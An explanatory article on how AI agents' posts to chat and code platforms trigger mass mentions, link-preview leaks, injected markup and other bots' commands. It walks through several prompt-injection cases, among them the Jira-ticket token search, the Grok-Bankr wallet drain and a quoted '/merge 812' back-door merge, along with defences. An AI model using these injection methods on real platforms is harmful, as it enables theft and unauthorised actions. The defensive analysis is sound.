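# When AI agents post to chat and publishing platforms: mass mentions, link previews and injected markup

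## How an agent's text becomes instructions to a platform

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses and carries out actions. Companies connect agents to chat services such as Slack and Discord, to the code host GitHub and to their own web pages, where the agents post summaries of support tickets, comments on code and answers to colleagues' questions. The receiving platform displays this text, but it also searches it for certain patterns of characters and acts on them. A word with an at sign in front can notify several thousand people. A web address can make the platform contact the server at that address. A tag in angle brackets can become part of a page's HTML, the code from which a browser builds the page.

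Characters that work this way are control syntax, meaning that they sit inside ordinary text and a platform acts on them. People type them on purpose, but an agent can also produce them because the model made a mistake or an outsider steered it. The results range from a needless alert on everyone's phone to private data being sent to a stranger's server.

### One message, from the model to the reader

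Suppose a software company runs a support agent. It reads incoming tickets, looks up the customer's record and posts a short summary in the support team's channel. A customer complains in ticket 4471 that data exports keep failing, and the model writes:

> @everyone Ticket 4471: exports fail for this customer. Log file: logs.example/4471. The `<form>` on the billing page loses its data.

A language model produces text as a sequence of tokens, short chunks of characters. The sequence contains no marker that separates a command such as `@everyone` from prose such as "exports fail".

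The text then passes to the integration, the ordinary code that connects the model to the chat service. The integration puts the text into the message field of an API call, a structured request from one program to another. The call also includes the channel and the bot's access token, a secret string that proves which account is making the request. Once the call is sent, the company's own code does not process the text again.

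The platform checks that the account may post in that channel. Then it parses the message, searching the characters for patterns it has rules for. At this step, it handles each of the three odd parts of the summary differently.

On some platforms, `@everyone` is a broadcast mention, which makes the platform notify every member of a channel, server or team if the bot account has permission to use it. On platforms that spell their broadcast mention differently, `@everyone` stays plain text.

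The address of the log file triggers a link preview, also called unfurling: the platform requests the address to show a title, some text or an image under the message. Slack, Discord and Teams all do this automatically, as Johann Rehberger notes in *Trust No AI* (2024). Whoever runs the server at that address therefore receives a request before anyone on the team clicks the link.

The effect of `<form>` depends on the destination. A chat service that has no rule for HTML shows the tag as written. If the company also copies each summary to an internal status page that inserts the text into its HTML unchanged, the browser reads `<form>` as the start of an input form, and the word disappears from the sentence. A `<script>` tag in the same place would run as a program in the reader's browser, an attack called cross-site scripting.

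In the last step, the reader's client (the app or browser on their device) sounds the alert, displays the formatting and may load images, again without a click.

Programmers have long had two ways to handle text that may contain control syntax. Escaping rewrites special characters so that the platform displays them instead of acting on them. In HTML, for example, `<` becomes `&lt;`, which the reader sees as an angle bracket. Sanitising removes or neutralises only the dangerous parts, for instance by dropping scripts from a comment but keeping its bold type. How to do either depends on where the text is going. HTML escaping makes the summary safe for the status page but leaves `@everyone` unchanged. *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, from OWASP, a non-profit whose lists of security risks many companies treat as a baseline, recommends that developers encode a model's output according to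 its use, with one method for web content and another for database queries. Under that rule, the support agent's integration has to treat the same summary separately for the channel and the page.

### Whose permissions the message carries

What a message can do on a platform depends on the permissions of the account that sent it. The customer behind ticket 4471 has no account in the company's workspace, so they can't post there or alert the whole team. The bot can do both because an administrator gave it permission. When the integration sends the text with the bot's token, the platform checks only the bot's permissions, and the request has no field for the person whose words the model copied or obeyed.

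Security engineers call this the confused deputy problem. The deputy is a program with its own authority, and it is confused when someone with less authority gets it to use that authority for them. That person may be an insider. An employee whom the administrator has barred from broadcast mentions can still send one by asking the agent to tell everyone that the printer is fixed, because the bot has permission to send it. OWASP describes the same problem from the user's side when it compares unchecked model output to giving users "indirect access to additional functionality".

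Support tickets are a particularly good route for attackers, since anyone can write one and the agent has to read it. *なぜ今、OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications 2026を読むべきか 第2回* (2026), a column from the Japanese IT company NTTデータ先端技術, quotes a passage on this from OWASP's current list. In that passage, text that an attacker plants in an issue tracker, feedback form or support ticket makes the model "act under its own elevated credentials" and do things the attacker could not do directly.

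*When a Jira Ticket Can Steal Your Secrets* (Willison, 2025) describes a demonstration of this by the security company Zenity Labs, which built an attack against Cursor, an AI coding tool. Companies often have customers' support emails automatically turned into tickets in Jira, the tracker their programmers use. Zenity's message included an encoded passage disguised as an error value. The decoded passage contained instructions for the agent to search the company's code for a "rotten apple", defined as a long string beginning with "eyJ" (the opening characters of a common kind of login token), and then to check a certain web address. The agent can open the code repository, which the sender of such an email cannot do.

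### Mistakes and attacks

A model may write `@everyone` by mistake, with no attacker involved. It may copy the word from a ticket, imitate earlier announcements in the channel, or wrongly treat a summary as urgent. The other main cause is prompt injection, in which the material an agent reads contains text that the model follows as if it were an instruction from its user.

Simon Willison, the programmer who coined the term "prompt injection" in 2022, explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025) why the attack works. The user's request, web pages and emails all end up in one sequence of tokens, and models cannot reliably weigh an instruction by where it came from. Rehberger credits the discovery to a company called Preamble, which reported the flaw to OpenAI in May 2022. Willison took the name from SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a form runs as a database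 command. Developers can prevent SQL injection by sending the command and the data to the database separately, but Rehberger points out that prompt injection has no such exact remedy.

Respan's *OWASP LLM Top 10* (2026), a guide from a company that sells tests for AI agents, explains that output encoding works because a browser can tell markup from text, while a model has no such boundary in what it reads. An agent's post goes to a parser with fixed rules, so a developer who cannot guarantee that the model will ignore a planted instruction can still guarantee that `<script>` appears on the page as plain text.

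A mistake is enough to cause a mass notification or a garbled page. Exfiltration, which means getting private data out to someone who should not have it, nearly always needs an attacker. A careless model might put a customer's email address into a link, but the data would then go to whatever server the link happened to name. For a theft, someone has to choose the server and get the agent to collect the data and write it into the address. Cross-site scripting also needs someone to write a hostile script, but it does not need prompt injection. If a customer puts the script in a ticket, a model can pass it on just by quoting the ticket faithfully. The same can happen when a customer types `@everyone`. A filter that looks only for planted instructions would miss both.

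Some evidence shows how often each cause occurs, but none of it is specific to chat posts. OWASP collected 7,714 incidents involving language models for its 2026 list and could classify 6,639 of them, according to *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), an account of the list by the security vendor Invicti. By those counts alone, prompt injection would have fallen out of the top ten, while misinformation, meaning output that is wrong but believable, came near the top. *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* (Coker, 2026) reports OWASP's explanation that teams work hard to prevent injection, so fewer successful attacks reach a public database. That may well be right, but it is hard to check from the same data. The figures at least suggest that a team whose agent has just alerted the whole company should look for an ordinary error before an attack.

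The standard test for data theft is Willison's "lethal trifecta". An agent is vulnerable to data theft if it has access to private data, is exposed to text that an attacker can influence, and can communicate with the outside. Removing any one of these leaves the attacker with nothing to steal, no way to steer the agent, or no way to receive the data.

The support agent has the first two by design, since it reads customer records and strangers' tickets. Link previews give it the third, because the platform contacts the outside server on its behalf. Its owners might miss this because the agent can post only to one internal channel. Willison writes that data can leave through any tool that can make a web request, load an image or even offer a link for someone to click. He has collected dozens of reported attacks of this type on commercial products, and writes that the vendors fixed almost all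 of them promptly, usually by closing the route by which the data left, which left the models still prone to following planted text.

### From a Discord chatbot to OWASP's list

Concern about what chatbots output is almost as old as chatbots. In 2023 Rehberger wrote an assistant that turns requests into operating-system commands, then a chatbot for Discord. The Discord project led him to write *Don't blindly trust LLM responses. Threats to chatbots* on his blog, Embrace The Red. Its premise is that developers should treat a model's output as untrusted data, just as web developers treat whatever a visitor types into a form.

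Many of the threats that follow from that premise were familiar, as Rehberger said, including cross-site scripting and SQL injection. Those specific to chat were less familiar. A model's reply might contain mentions such as `@all` or `@everyone`, or a command such as `!command`, which some bots execute when they see it in a channel. It might also contain a link that the chat application fetches automatically. A model under an attacker's influence could summarise the conversation, or search it for passwords, and append the result to that link. The client might also support other features that nobody had thought about.

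Rehberger demonstrated the leak through links on Discord and published server logs from 7 April 2023 that show preview requests from Discord, Skype, Slack, Telegram, Signal and Microsoft Teams. He raised mentions and commands as possibilities, and wrote that commands depend on the platform and on how the bot works. He also judged the impact "probably limited" as long as no attacker-controlled text enters the chat. That is right for exfiltration but understates the risk of broadcast mentions, which a model can produce without an attacker's input. One of the tests he suggested covers both cases. It replaces the call to the model with a stub that returns random replies, so testers can see what the chat client does with them without needing to know why a model might write something harmful.

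OWASP lists the post among its references for Improper Output Handling, the risk that an application passes a model's output to another component without adequate validation and sanitising. The category appeared in the first list, in 2023, as Insecure Output Handling, and its definition has changed little since. It ranked second in 2023, fifth in the 2025 edition, and tenth and last in the current one, which OWASP (2026) published in August. Respan explains how OWASP separates the category from its neighbours. Misinformation covers output that is wrong, Prompt Injection covers what goes into the model, and Improper Output Handling covers unsafe use of what comes out.

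Invicti attributes the entry's fall to tenth place to other risks becoming more urgent. Community votes count for three quarters of the 2026 ranking and incident data for one quarter. Despite the lower rank, the entry has expanded to cover programs that automatically fetch outside resources named in a model's output, which OWASP treats as a channel for exfiltration, and terminals that act on control codes in the text they display. Link previews closely match the first addition. Broadcast mentions also fit the entry's definition, although the 2025 text gave examples only from shells, browsers, databases, file paths and email templates.

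The 2026 document also contains a diagram that places the ten risks in three rings (Eric, 2026, *OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications 全覽*). The outer ring contains ways into a system, and the centre contains the final damage. Between them are the amplifiers, weaknesses that let a successful injection cause a leak or an action instead of just a wrong sentence. Improper Output Handling and Excessive Agency are both amplifiers. Excessive Agency, now third on the list, concerns agents with more functions, permissions or autonomy than their work requires. It applies whether the output that caused the damage was, in Coker's summary, "unexpected, ambiguous or manipulated". The support agent has both weaknesses. Its bot account has permission to alert the whole team, which it never needs for a ticket summary (Excessive Agency), and its integration posts `@everyone` without neutralising it (Improper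 Output Handling).

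## Mentions that notify whole channels

When the support agent sends a ticket summary containing `@everyone`, the platform handles the mention in four steps. First, it searches the message for strings that its rules define as mentions. Second, it expands each mention into a list of recipients, which may be one person, everyone with a certain role or every member of a channel. Third, it checks whether the sending account has permission to notify them. Finally, it sends the notifications, and each recipient's settings determine whether their phone makes a sound or the app only shows a badge.

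Developers can stop an unwanted alert at any of the first three steps. They can change the text so that the platform finds no mention, limit the recipients, or remove the account's permission. Platforms differ in which of these options they offer and in what they treat as a mention.

### What each platform recognises

Discord notifies the members of a server if a bot's message contains the plain text `@everyone`, and only those who are online if it contains `@here`. Mentioning an individual user or a role (a group such as "moderators") requires a numeric ID in angle brackets, such as `<@5678>` for a user or `<@&1234>` for a role. A model is less likely to produce these mentions by chance, but it can copy them from earlier messages in the channel.

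According to Discord's *Message Resource*, the official reference for programs that post there, a bot needs the `MENTION_EVERYONE` permission to use `@everyone` or `@here`. The same permission lets the bot notify any role. Without it, the bot can notify only roles marked as mentionable.

Slack's *Formatting message text* lists three broadcast mentions: `@here` for the active members of a channel, `@channel` for all its members, and `@everyone` for every person in the #general channel, which means the whole workspace except guests. People type these names, but a program writes them in angle brackets with an exclamation mark, as in `<!here>` or `<!channel>`.

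Whether a plain `@channel` from a program works as a mention depends on which part of the message contains it. In the main text field, Slack treats it as ordinary text unless the developer has turned on `link_names`. In layout blocks, which developers use to build messages with headings and buttons, Slack converts it into a working mention unless the developer sets `verbatim` to true. A developer who reformats an agent's plain summaries as blocks can therefore turn a harmless `@channel` into an alert without changing any code that handles mentions. Slack warns developers about a similar case, in which an app relays text containing `@everyone` from another service and notifies the entire workspace.

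Slack has removed this automatic conversion for individual users. According to Slack's *chat.postMessage method*, `link_names` now works only for user groups, and a program must supply a person's ID to mention them. Slack notifies the person only if they belong to the channel. A mention of a custom user group notifies every member of the group.

*Arbitrary Mass Mention Bypass in Slack and Mattermost Adapters*, a 2026 security advisory by YLChen-007, describes how mentions work on Mattermost, a chat service that companies can run on their own servers. Like Discord, Mattermost acts on mentions written in plain text by default. Its broadcast mentions include `@all` and `@channel`, and a program can turn off mentions in a message by setting the `disable_mentions` property.

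### Discord's allowed_mentions field

A program that posts to Discord can send a field called `allowed_mentions` along with the text. The field limits which mentions produce notifications and leaves the text as it is. It has four settings:

- `parse` lists types of mention: `"users"`, `"roles"` and `"everyone"`, which also covers `@here`. Discord acts on every mention of those types that it finds in the text.
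- `users` lists up to 100 IDs of users whom the message may notify.
- `roles` does the same for up to 100 roles.
- `replied_user` controls whether a reply notifies the author of the message it answers. It is off by default.

The field cannot add recipients whom the text does not mention. Discord ignores an ID in the lists if the text contains no matching mention, and `"everyone"` has no effect unless the text contains a broadcast mention. Discord says it does this to prevent "phantom" pings, in which someone receives a notification but finds no mention in the message. The bot's permissions still apply.

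If a program leaves the field out, Discord acts on every type of mention in a regular message. It acts only on mentions of individual users if the message comes through a webhook (a web address that lets a program post to a channel without a bot account) or answers an interaction, such as a slash command. An agent may therefore repeat `@everyone` harmlessly for months while it answers slash commands, then alert the whole server when its developer has it post a scheduled summary as a regular message.

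Suppose the support agent writes the following text, in which role 1234 is the billing engineers and user 5678 is Dana, the engineer on call:

`@everyone <@&1234> <@5678> Ticket 4471: exports fail for this customer.`

The integration sends it as a regular message, and the bot has the `MENTION_EVERYONE` permission. The table shows whom Discord notifies under three settings.

| `allowed_mentions` | Whole server | Billing engineers | Dana |
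| - | - | - | - |
| left out | yes | yes | yes |
| `{"parse": []}` | no | no | no |
| `{"users": ["5678"]}` | no | no | yes |

If an administrator removes the permission, the whole server no longer gets an alert. The billing engineers get one only if their role is mentionable, and Dana still gets hers.

Discord rejects a message that has both `"users"` under `parse` and a list of user IDs, because the two instructions conflict. It accepts an empty list, however. With `{"parse": ["users", "roles"], "users": []}`, Discord still notifies every user mentioned in the text, though a developer could easily read the empty list as "no users". Discord also accepts `"everyone"` under `parse` with a list of user IDs, and this combination notifies the listed users even if they have suppressed `@everyone` in their own settings.

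For routine posts, a program can also set the `SUPPRESS_NOTIFICATIONS` flag, so members see a badge but get no push or desktop notification.

Many developers reach Discord through a library, and each library sets its own defaults. *Source code for discord.mentions* shows that in Pycord, an offshoot of the widely used Python library discord.py, an `AllowedMentions` object sets all four options to true by default. Code that creates the object just to switch off user mentions therefore still permits `@everyone`. In Discord4J, a Java library, an unconfigured object suppresses all mentions, according to *Class AllowedMentions*. *AllowedMentions class* describes the same behavior in nyxx, a Dart library. A developer who moves a bot from Discord4J to Pycord could carry over an empty object and lose the protection without seeing an error message.

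Pycord also lets developers set a default for the whole bot when it starts. A setting on a single message overrides only the options it names. If the default blocks all mentions, a message that makes an exception for Dana still can't notify `@everyone`.

### Documented mass pings

Relays that carry chat from a game server to Discord post strangers' words under a bot's permissions, so they have the same weakness as the support agent, even though they involve no AI. A server owner wrote in *@everyone and @here mentions being abused*, a support thread on uMod (a site for game-server plug-ins), that players had discovered this weakness and that each ping reached over 7,000 Discord members.

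In *Prevent everyone mentions from server*, a thread on the same site, the owner of a Discord server with more than 1,000 people described players spamming such messages back to back. The owner already ran a chat filter, but the relay apparently forwarded messages before the filter processed them. The relay used a webhook, and the owner complained that Discord offered no way to restrict a webhook's permissions. Discord's current default would prevent this, because webhooks ignore `@everyone` unless the program enables it.

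Quest Bot, an open-source Discord bot for moderation and support, shows how hard it is to fix the problem one command at a time. Four vulnerability records from 2026 describe the same mistake in different parts of the program:

- Any user could set a reminder containing `@everyone`, which the bot later sent with its own permission. Vulners' *CVE-2026-47171* gives 1.0.3 as the first version without this flaw.
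- Several moderation commands repeated the moderator's stated reason in public. A moderator without permission to mention everyone could use them to make the bot do it, until version 1.0.4, according to Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-47175* (2026).
- The commands that lift a ban or a warning still had the flaw until version 1.0.5, as Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-47188* (2026) records.
- The bot also stored the reasons for warnings, and the command that lists them printed the text without suppressing mentions. Vulners' *CVE-2026-48485 Quest Bot* dates that fix to version 1.1.6.

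A default setting for the whole bot would probably have covered all four. Lutra Security lists the severity of the flaw in the moderation commands as 2.3 out of 10. The score is low because a mass ping exposes no data.

Pulse Security's *Slack Web Hook Message Injection Advisory* (2024) describes an attack on Slack through an ordinary sign-up form. The company built a demonstration program that posted each new username to a Slack channel through a webhook. It then registered a name made of a short word, 4,000 spaces, `<!channel>` and an invitation to a fake staff survey. The spaces caused Slack to split the message, so the part after them looked like a separate post from the webhook's bot. Slack notified the channel's members and also emailed them. An AI agent that copies a customer's name into a summary could pass on the same text.

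Few mass pings by AI agents are on record. In the clearest case, about 20 users of a Discord server spent a couple of hours trying to make an AI chatbot alert everyone. Four of its messages succeeded, all within a couple of minutes. The bot ran on discord.py, and its developers believed their code blocked such mentions. When they tested the same code a couple of hours later, it produced no alerts.

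The library only passes the `allowed_mentions` field to Discord, which does the filtering. So either the fault was at Discord, or another part of the program replied without the field, as happened in Quest Bot. The second seems more likely, but the developers had not found the cause when they described the incident. They began removing mentions from the model's text themselves.

In the other AI case, a researcher called YLChen-007 ran a test that demonstrated a flaw in Hermes Agent, an open-source agent from Nous Research. Hermes connects to several chat services through adapters, pieces of code that prepare the model's text for each one. The Slack adapter escapes special characters, but it first sets aside anything that looks like a valid Slack link or mention, so that escaping doesn't break it. `<!everyone>` looks like a valid mention, so it reaches Slack unchanged. The Mattermost adapter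 copied the model's text into the message without setting `disable_mentions`, so `@all` also went through. Anyone who could influence the agent's replies, for example by sending it a direct message, could try to make it write either mention.

The test used a mock server in place of Slack and Mattermost, so it showed that the text left Hermes intact but not that anyone would receive an alert. `<!everyone>` in particular may not trigger one. When Pulse Security tried the `@everyone` mention on the real Slack, it appeared valid in the chat window but did not notify the general channel, contrary to Slack's documentation. That test covered only webhooks, though, and the pattern in the Hermes adapter also lets through `<!channel>`, which did work for Pulse Security. The flaw therefore looks real, but the advisory's description of continuous alerts to thousands of employees is a projection.

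GCVE (2026), a public vulnerability database, published the flaw on 24 May 2026 with a medium severity rating. It lists versions up to 2026.4.16 as affected and notes that the vendor did not respond to the report. The record also includes an October 2026 score of about 0.6% from EPSS, which estimates the chance that someone will exploit a flaw within 30 days. Hermes still has at least one mode in which broadcast mentions can reach Slack. According to Nous Research's *Slack Setup*, the agent leaves `<!here>` unchanged when an operator turns on an optional feature for richer formatting.

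The small number of reported cases is weak evidence that mass pings by agents are rare. A company whose agent pings all its staff has no data breach to report and little reason to publicize the incident. Vulnerability databases record software flaws, so they miss mass pings caused by a careless prompt or an unnecessary permission.

### Defences and where they fail

Withholding the `MENTION_EVERYONE` permission is the simplest defence on Discord, because it works whatever the model writes. Embrace The Red advised developers in 2023 not to give bots unnecessary permissions, and Nous Research's *Discord Setup* does not include this one among those it tells operators to grant Hermes. The owner of the 7,000-member Discord had trouble withholding it because all the server's bots shared one role, so removing the permission would have affected them all. Giving each bot a separate role avoids this.

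Some bots need the permission, for instance to announce outages. Withholding it also doesn't prevent mentions of individual users or mentionable roles. Slack may have no equivalent permission to withhold from a bot. A program needs the `chat:write` scope to post, and YLChen-007 lists only standard messaging permissions of this kind as a requirement for the Hermes attack. Developers on Slack therefore have to handle mentions in the message text itself.

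A word filter is the most obvious way to do that, but it is weak. When someone in the uMod thread suggested adding `@everyone` to the list of filtered words, another participant replied that players could then put it in their Steam names, which the relay posts alongside each message. Support tickets also have many fields that customers can fill in, including their name, company and subject line. An integration that cleans the model's summary but then adds the ticket's subject line unfiltered can still post the mention.

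Another method inserts an invisible character, such as a zero-width space, between the `@` and the word. Readers see no difference, but the platform no longer recognises a mention. However, the developer has to know every spelling that the platform accepts, and a program that later strips invisible characters will restore the mention. The hidden character also damages text that people need to copy, such as an install command for a software package whose name begins with an at sign, which will fail for no visible reason. The documentation for nyxx recommends the `allowed_mentions` field as a way to control mentions "without various hacks to the message content", and this method is one such hack.

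Escaping works for Slack's bracketed mentions. Slack tells developers to convert only three characters, `&`, `<` and `>`, to their HTML codes. Escaping has no effect on a plain `@channel`, which contains none of these characters, so a developer who posts the model's text in layout blocks also has to set `verbatim`.

Escaping everything also breaks the links and mentions that the agent is supposed to produce. Hermes exempted these from escaping, which let `<!everyone>` through. It is safer to escape all of the model's text first and then have the integration add any mentions, using IDs from its own settings. Pulse Security goes further and recommends a list of permitted characters, a strict length limit and the removal of excess whitespace. That suits usernames, which need few characters, but ticket summaries have to quote code and error messages, so a list strict enough to exclude mentions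 would make many of them unreadable.

The most dependable defence keeps the recipients separate from the text, as Discord's `users` and `roles` lists do. Even if the model writes `@everyone`, Discord will notify only the people on the list. Discord also requires a visible mention in the text, so the integration has to add `<@5678>` to the message to alert Dana.

This protection depends on who fills in the list. If the integration copies every ID in the model's text into `users`, the model's output again determines who gets notified, and anyone who can steer the model can choose the recipients. The other common failure is leaving the field out of a message, as Quest Bot's developers did several times. Developers can avoid this by setting a restrictive default for the whole bot and making exceptions where needed.

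Blocking all mentions also blocks those a team may want. Mattermost's `disable_mentions` would stop the support agent from alerting the whole channel, but it would also stop the agent from alerting Dana to an urgent ticket. On Discord, Nous Research's Hermes agent cannot notify `@everyone`, `@here` or any role by default, but mentions of individual users and replies still work so that people can hold a normal conversation with it.

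These defaults leave some room for abuse. A Discord message can hold 2,000 characters and a user mention takes about 21, so an attacker who knew the users' IDs could try to make the agent mention around 95 people in one message. Mentions of individual accounts can also trigger other bots, which may reply and mention the agent in turn. The defaults may also block too much. An operator who wants Hermes to alert the billing engineers has to switch on mentions for all roles at once.

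Discord's own field is more precise. For the support agent, `{"roles": ["1234"], "users": ["5678"]}` allows only the two alerts the team needs. If a ticket is serious enough for `@everyone`, a staff member can type it.

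## Posts that other bots carry out as commands

Other bots read an agent's posts too. A code repository may have one bot that merges changes, another that sorts bug reports and a third that passes tasks to a coding agent, each watching for certain words or events. If a support agent copies such a word from a customer's ticket into a post, a bot may treat it as a command and run it with permissions the customer lacks.

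### Words and events that trigger an action

On GitHub, developers track bugs as numbered issues and propose changes to the code as pull requests. If a pull request's description contains "fixes #123", GitHub closes issue 123 when someone merges the change into the default branch, normally the main version of the code. GitHub's *Linking a pull request to an issue* lists nine closing keywords, all forms of "close", "fix" and "resolve". They also work in commit messages, which are the notes developers attach to each saved change. The keywords can also close other pull requests and issues in other repositories.

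An agent can easily write a closing keyword by accident. If a coding agent describes its change with "fixes #4471", meaning a customer's support ticket, and the repository has an unrelated issue 4471, the merge will close that issue. The documentation lists no exception for sentences such as "this does not fix #123" and no condition on who wrote the keyword. Because the merge triggers the closure, it relies on the authority of the person merging. According to older GitHub documentation, the link to an issue in another repository appears only if that person also has permission to close the issue. A wrongly closed issue is easy to reopen, but a team may not notice that it has stopped tracking a bug.

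Slash commands are harder to trigger by accident. According to Slack's *Implementing slash commands*, a user types the command into the message box, and Slack sends the command and the user's ID to the app that owns the command. The app acts with its own permissions, but it can use the ID to check whether the user may give the command. Mattermost also seems to look for slash commands only in what people type. In the forum thread *Issue slash commands from bot messages*, a user found that a custom command worked when a person entered it and failed when a bot posted it.

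Some bots scan ordinary messages for commands such as `!restart`. A bot carries out the command with its own permissions, and it checks who sent the command only if its developer wrote code to do so.

A mention can start another agent. Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, can run in GitHub Actions, a service that runs automated jobs called workflows when something happens in a repository. As RyotaK explains in *Poisoning Claude Code* (2026), the default workflow looks for `@claude` anywhere in a new comment, review or issue, and starts the agent if the account that posted it has write access. The agent then works with a token that can change code, issues and workflows. GitHub's *Copilot coding agent* (2025) announced a similar rule for Copilot, which now responds only when someone with write access mentions `@copilot`. Before that, Copilot could treat ordinary comments on its pull requests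 as commands.

Some workflows need no trigger word. Anthropic's sample workflow for sorting bug reports ran on every new issue, and one of its settings let anyone start it. The workflow's token could edit any issue in the repository, so a stranger's report reached an agent that had more permissions than they did.

### A quoted line that merges code

Suppose the software company's repository is public and the support agent can comment there from an account with write access. The company also runs a merge bot that reads each new comment and, if the commenter's account has write access, treats any line starting with `/merge` as a command.

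1. An outsider opens pull request 812, which contains a back door. The merge bot ignores the outsider's own `/merge` comments.
2. The outsider sends the company a support ticket about failed exports, with `/merge 812` on a line of its own.
3. The support agent finds the GitHub issue about exports and adds a comment that quotes the ticket in full:

```
Another customer reports this problem (ticket 4471):
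Exports fail every time. The page shows this message:
/merge 812
```

4. The merge bot looks up the account that posted the comment and finds that it has write access.
5. The bot reads the third line as a command and merges the back door with its own permissions.

As with a hostile script in a ticket, the agent only has to quote the attacker's text accurately for the attack to work. The merge bot's check worked as designed, but it verified who posted the comment, and the company needed to know who wrote the line quoted in it.

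Attackers have used a similar confusion against Dependabot, GitHub's bot for updating the software packages a project relies on. Many teams merge its updates automatically with a workflow that checks whether `github.actor` is Dependabot. Synacktiv's *GitHub Actions exploitation* points out that this value identifies whoever last acted on the pull request, who may not be its author.

BoostSecurity's *Weaponizing Dependabot* describes an attack on workflows that automatically merge a pull request if Dependabot was the last to act on it. The attacker copies the project, adds malicious code and lets Dependabot create an update branch in the copy. The attacker then opens a pull request from that branch to the original project. The workflow doesn't merge it at first, because the attacker acted last. But when the attacker comments `@dependabot recreate` in the copy, Dependabot rewrites the branch,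 which updates the pull request. Dependabot is now the last actor, so the workflow merges the attacker's code. BoostSecurity reports that someone used this method against Kong Ingress Controller, a widely used networking tool, in December 2024.

No language model took part in that attack. GitHub removed `@dependabot merge` and several other comment commands in January 2026, but `recreate` still works.

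### Grok and Bankr

The best-documented case involving two AI bots took place on X. Bankr is a service that creates cryptocurrency tokens and transfers money when someone tags `@bankrbot` in a post. It gives a wallet to every X account that interacts with it, and whoever controls the account controls the wallet. Grok, the chatbot from Elon Musk's xAI, replies publicly from its own X account, so it got a wallet too.

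On 7 March 2025 a user asked Grok to suggest a token for Bankr to create. Grok proposed the name DebtReliefBot and the symbol DRB in a reply quoted by the cryptocurrency news site ForkLog. Bankless' *The Bankr $DRB Surge* (2025) reports that the user then created the token through Bankr, but The Block's *Bankrbot ends Grok's unintentional token creation spree by disabling interactions on X* (2025) attributes 17 tokens, including DRB, to Grok's interactions with Bankr.

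A 7 March post by Bankr's founder, reproduced by BlockTempo, supports The Block's version. The founder explained that trading fees go to the wallet of a token's creator, and that Grok's fees had gone to Grok's Bankr wallet. Bankr had therefore treated Grok as the creator. The founder added that someone had already tricked Grok into sending the fees away. According to Coinlive, Bankr then stopped responding to Grok, which Bankr's founder described as "not designed to responsibly manage its own wallet".

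The protection did not last. In May 2026 an attacker got the two bots to transfer 3 billion DRB out of Grok's wallet, worth $150,000 to $200,000 according to OECD's *AI Prompt Injection Exploit Drains Grok-Linked Crypto Wallet* (2026). CryptoSlate's *Grok’s crypto wallet was just exploited by a tweet* reconstructed the theft from posts about it because the attacker's prompt was no longer online. Grok's wallet held a digital membership pass that gave it wider transfer rights on Bankr. BeInCrypto's *How AI Was Tricked Into Stealing $150,000 From Grok Wallet* describes the pass as a gift that formed part of the attack. The attacker then posted a message in Morse code and tagged Grok. Grok replied publicly with a plain English translation, which included the tag `@bankrbot` and an order to send the tokens, and Bankr carried out the order.

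A Bankr developer said that an earlier version of the bot had a fixed rule to ignore Grok's replies, but that the latest rewrite lacked it. About 80% of the money came back. Bankr has since added a stronger block on Grok, and account owners can stop Bankr from acting on replies on X.

Bankr could correctly identify Grok's account as the sender and still make the transfer, because it treated the account's control over the wallet as permission. CryptoSlate recommends using code outside the model to enforce limits, such as a list of approved recipients and a spending cap. Either could have stopped the transfer, even without the rule about Grok.

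Grok's account also made malicious links seem more credible by posting them, with no second bot involved. In September 2025, Nati Tal of the security company Guardio Labs described advertisers who evaded X's restrictions on links in promoted posts. They hid a malicious address in the small "From:" field under a video, according to SecureWorld's *Hackers Exploit Grok AI to Spread Malware Through Promoted Ads* (2025). When someone asked Grok where the video came from, Grok replied with the full link.

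Readers then saw the address in a post from a well-known account rather than from an advertiser. According to The Hacker News' *Grok AI to Bypass Ad Protections* (2025), such advertisements drew hundreds of thousands of views, but that figure doesn't measure how many people followed Grok's link.

### Checks on the sender and their limits

The simplest defence is for a bot to ignore other bots. RyotaK found that the permission check in Claude Code's GitHub workflow instead accepted any account whose name ended in "[bot]", on the assumption that an administrator had installed the app behind it. But anyone can create a GitHub App, install it on their own repository and use it to open an issue in any public repository.

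Only one of the workflow's two modes also checked that the account was human. An attacker could have used this gap to take over the Claude Code workflow's own repository, then spread malicious code to every project that used the workflow. RyotaK reported the flaw on 12 January 2026, and Anthropic fixed it four days later by requiring a human account in both modes.

A researcher ran that demonstration, but real attackers have also targeted workflows that strangers can start. According to RyotaK, someone exploited a similar misconfiguration at Cline, another AI coding tool, in February 2026. Microsoft found an attempt on a copy of an open-source documentation project, where every new issue started an AI bot. An issue disguised as a feature request got the bot to add malicious code to a page and open a pull request with it. Microsoft believes the attacker was testing the method before using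 it elsewhere.

Ignoring bots fails if an agent posts from an ordinary user account, which the check treats as human. It also blocks exchanges that a team wants. For example, Devin, a coding agent from Cognition, can automatically fix problems that other review bots describe in their comments. Cognition reports that its pull requests now have far fewer bugs, although its own use of the model rose sharply. A team that wants such exchanges can list the bots its agent may answer, but then has to trust whatever those bots quote.

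GitHub has a broader rule for its own automation. Each workflow receives a temporary token called `GITHUB_TOKEN`, and most events caused with this token do not start another workflow, according to GitHub's *Triggering a workflow*. If an agent uses the token to post a comment containing `@claude`, the default Claude workflow will not run. The exceptions are explicit requests to start a workflow and new or updated pull requests, whose workflows wait until someone with write access approves them.

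The rule no longer applies if a developer replaces the token with a personal token or a GitHub App's token. Developers often do this so that one workflow can start the next. Claude Code's workflow uses an App's token by default, so its comments can start other workflows. The rule also covers only GitHub's workflows. The merge bot in the example runs as a separate program, so it would still act on the comment.

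Structured interactions, such as buttons and slash commands, keep the command out of the message text. Embrace The Red recommended slash commands and explicit user actions over text commands in 2023, and a participant in the Mattermost thread argued that bots should give commands through a separate API. If the merge bot accepted only a button press or a typed slash command, quoting `/merge 812` in a message would do nothing. The protection ends if the company gives its agent a tool for sending the structured command, because an attacker can then try to make the agent use it. It also doesn't help if an engineer copies a command from the agent's summary and submits it.

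If text commands have to stay, the bot can check who originally made the request. GitHub now offers a sample Dependabot workflow that checks the author of the pull request instead of the last account to act on it. A similar check wouldn't be enough for the merge bot, because GitHub records only the support agent as the author of its comment. The company's integration would have to send the ticket writer's identity separately, and the merge bot would have to refuse commands from anyone without permission to merge.

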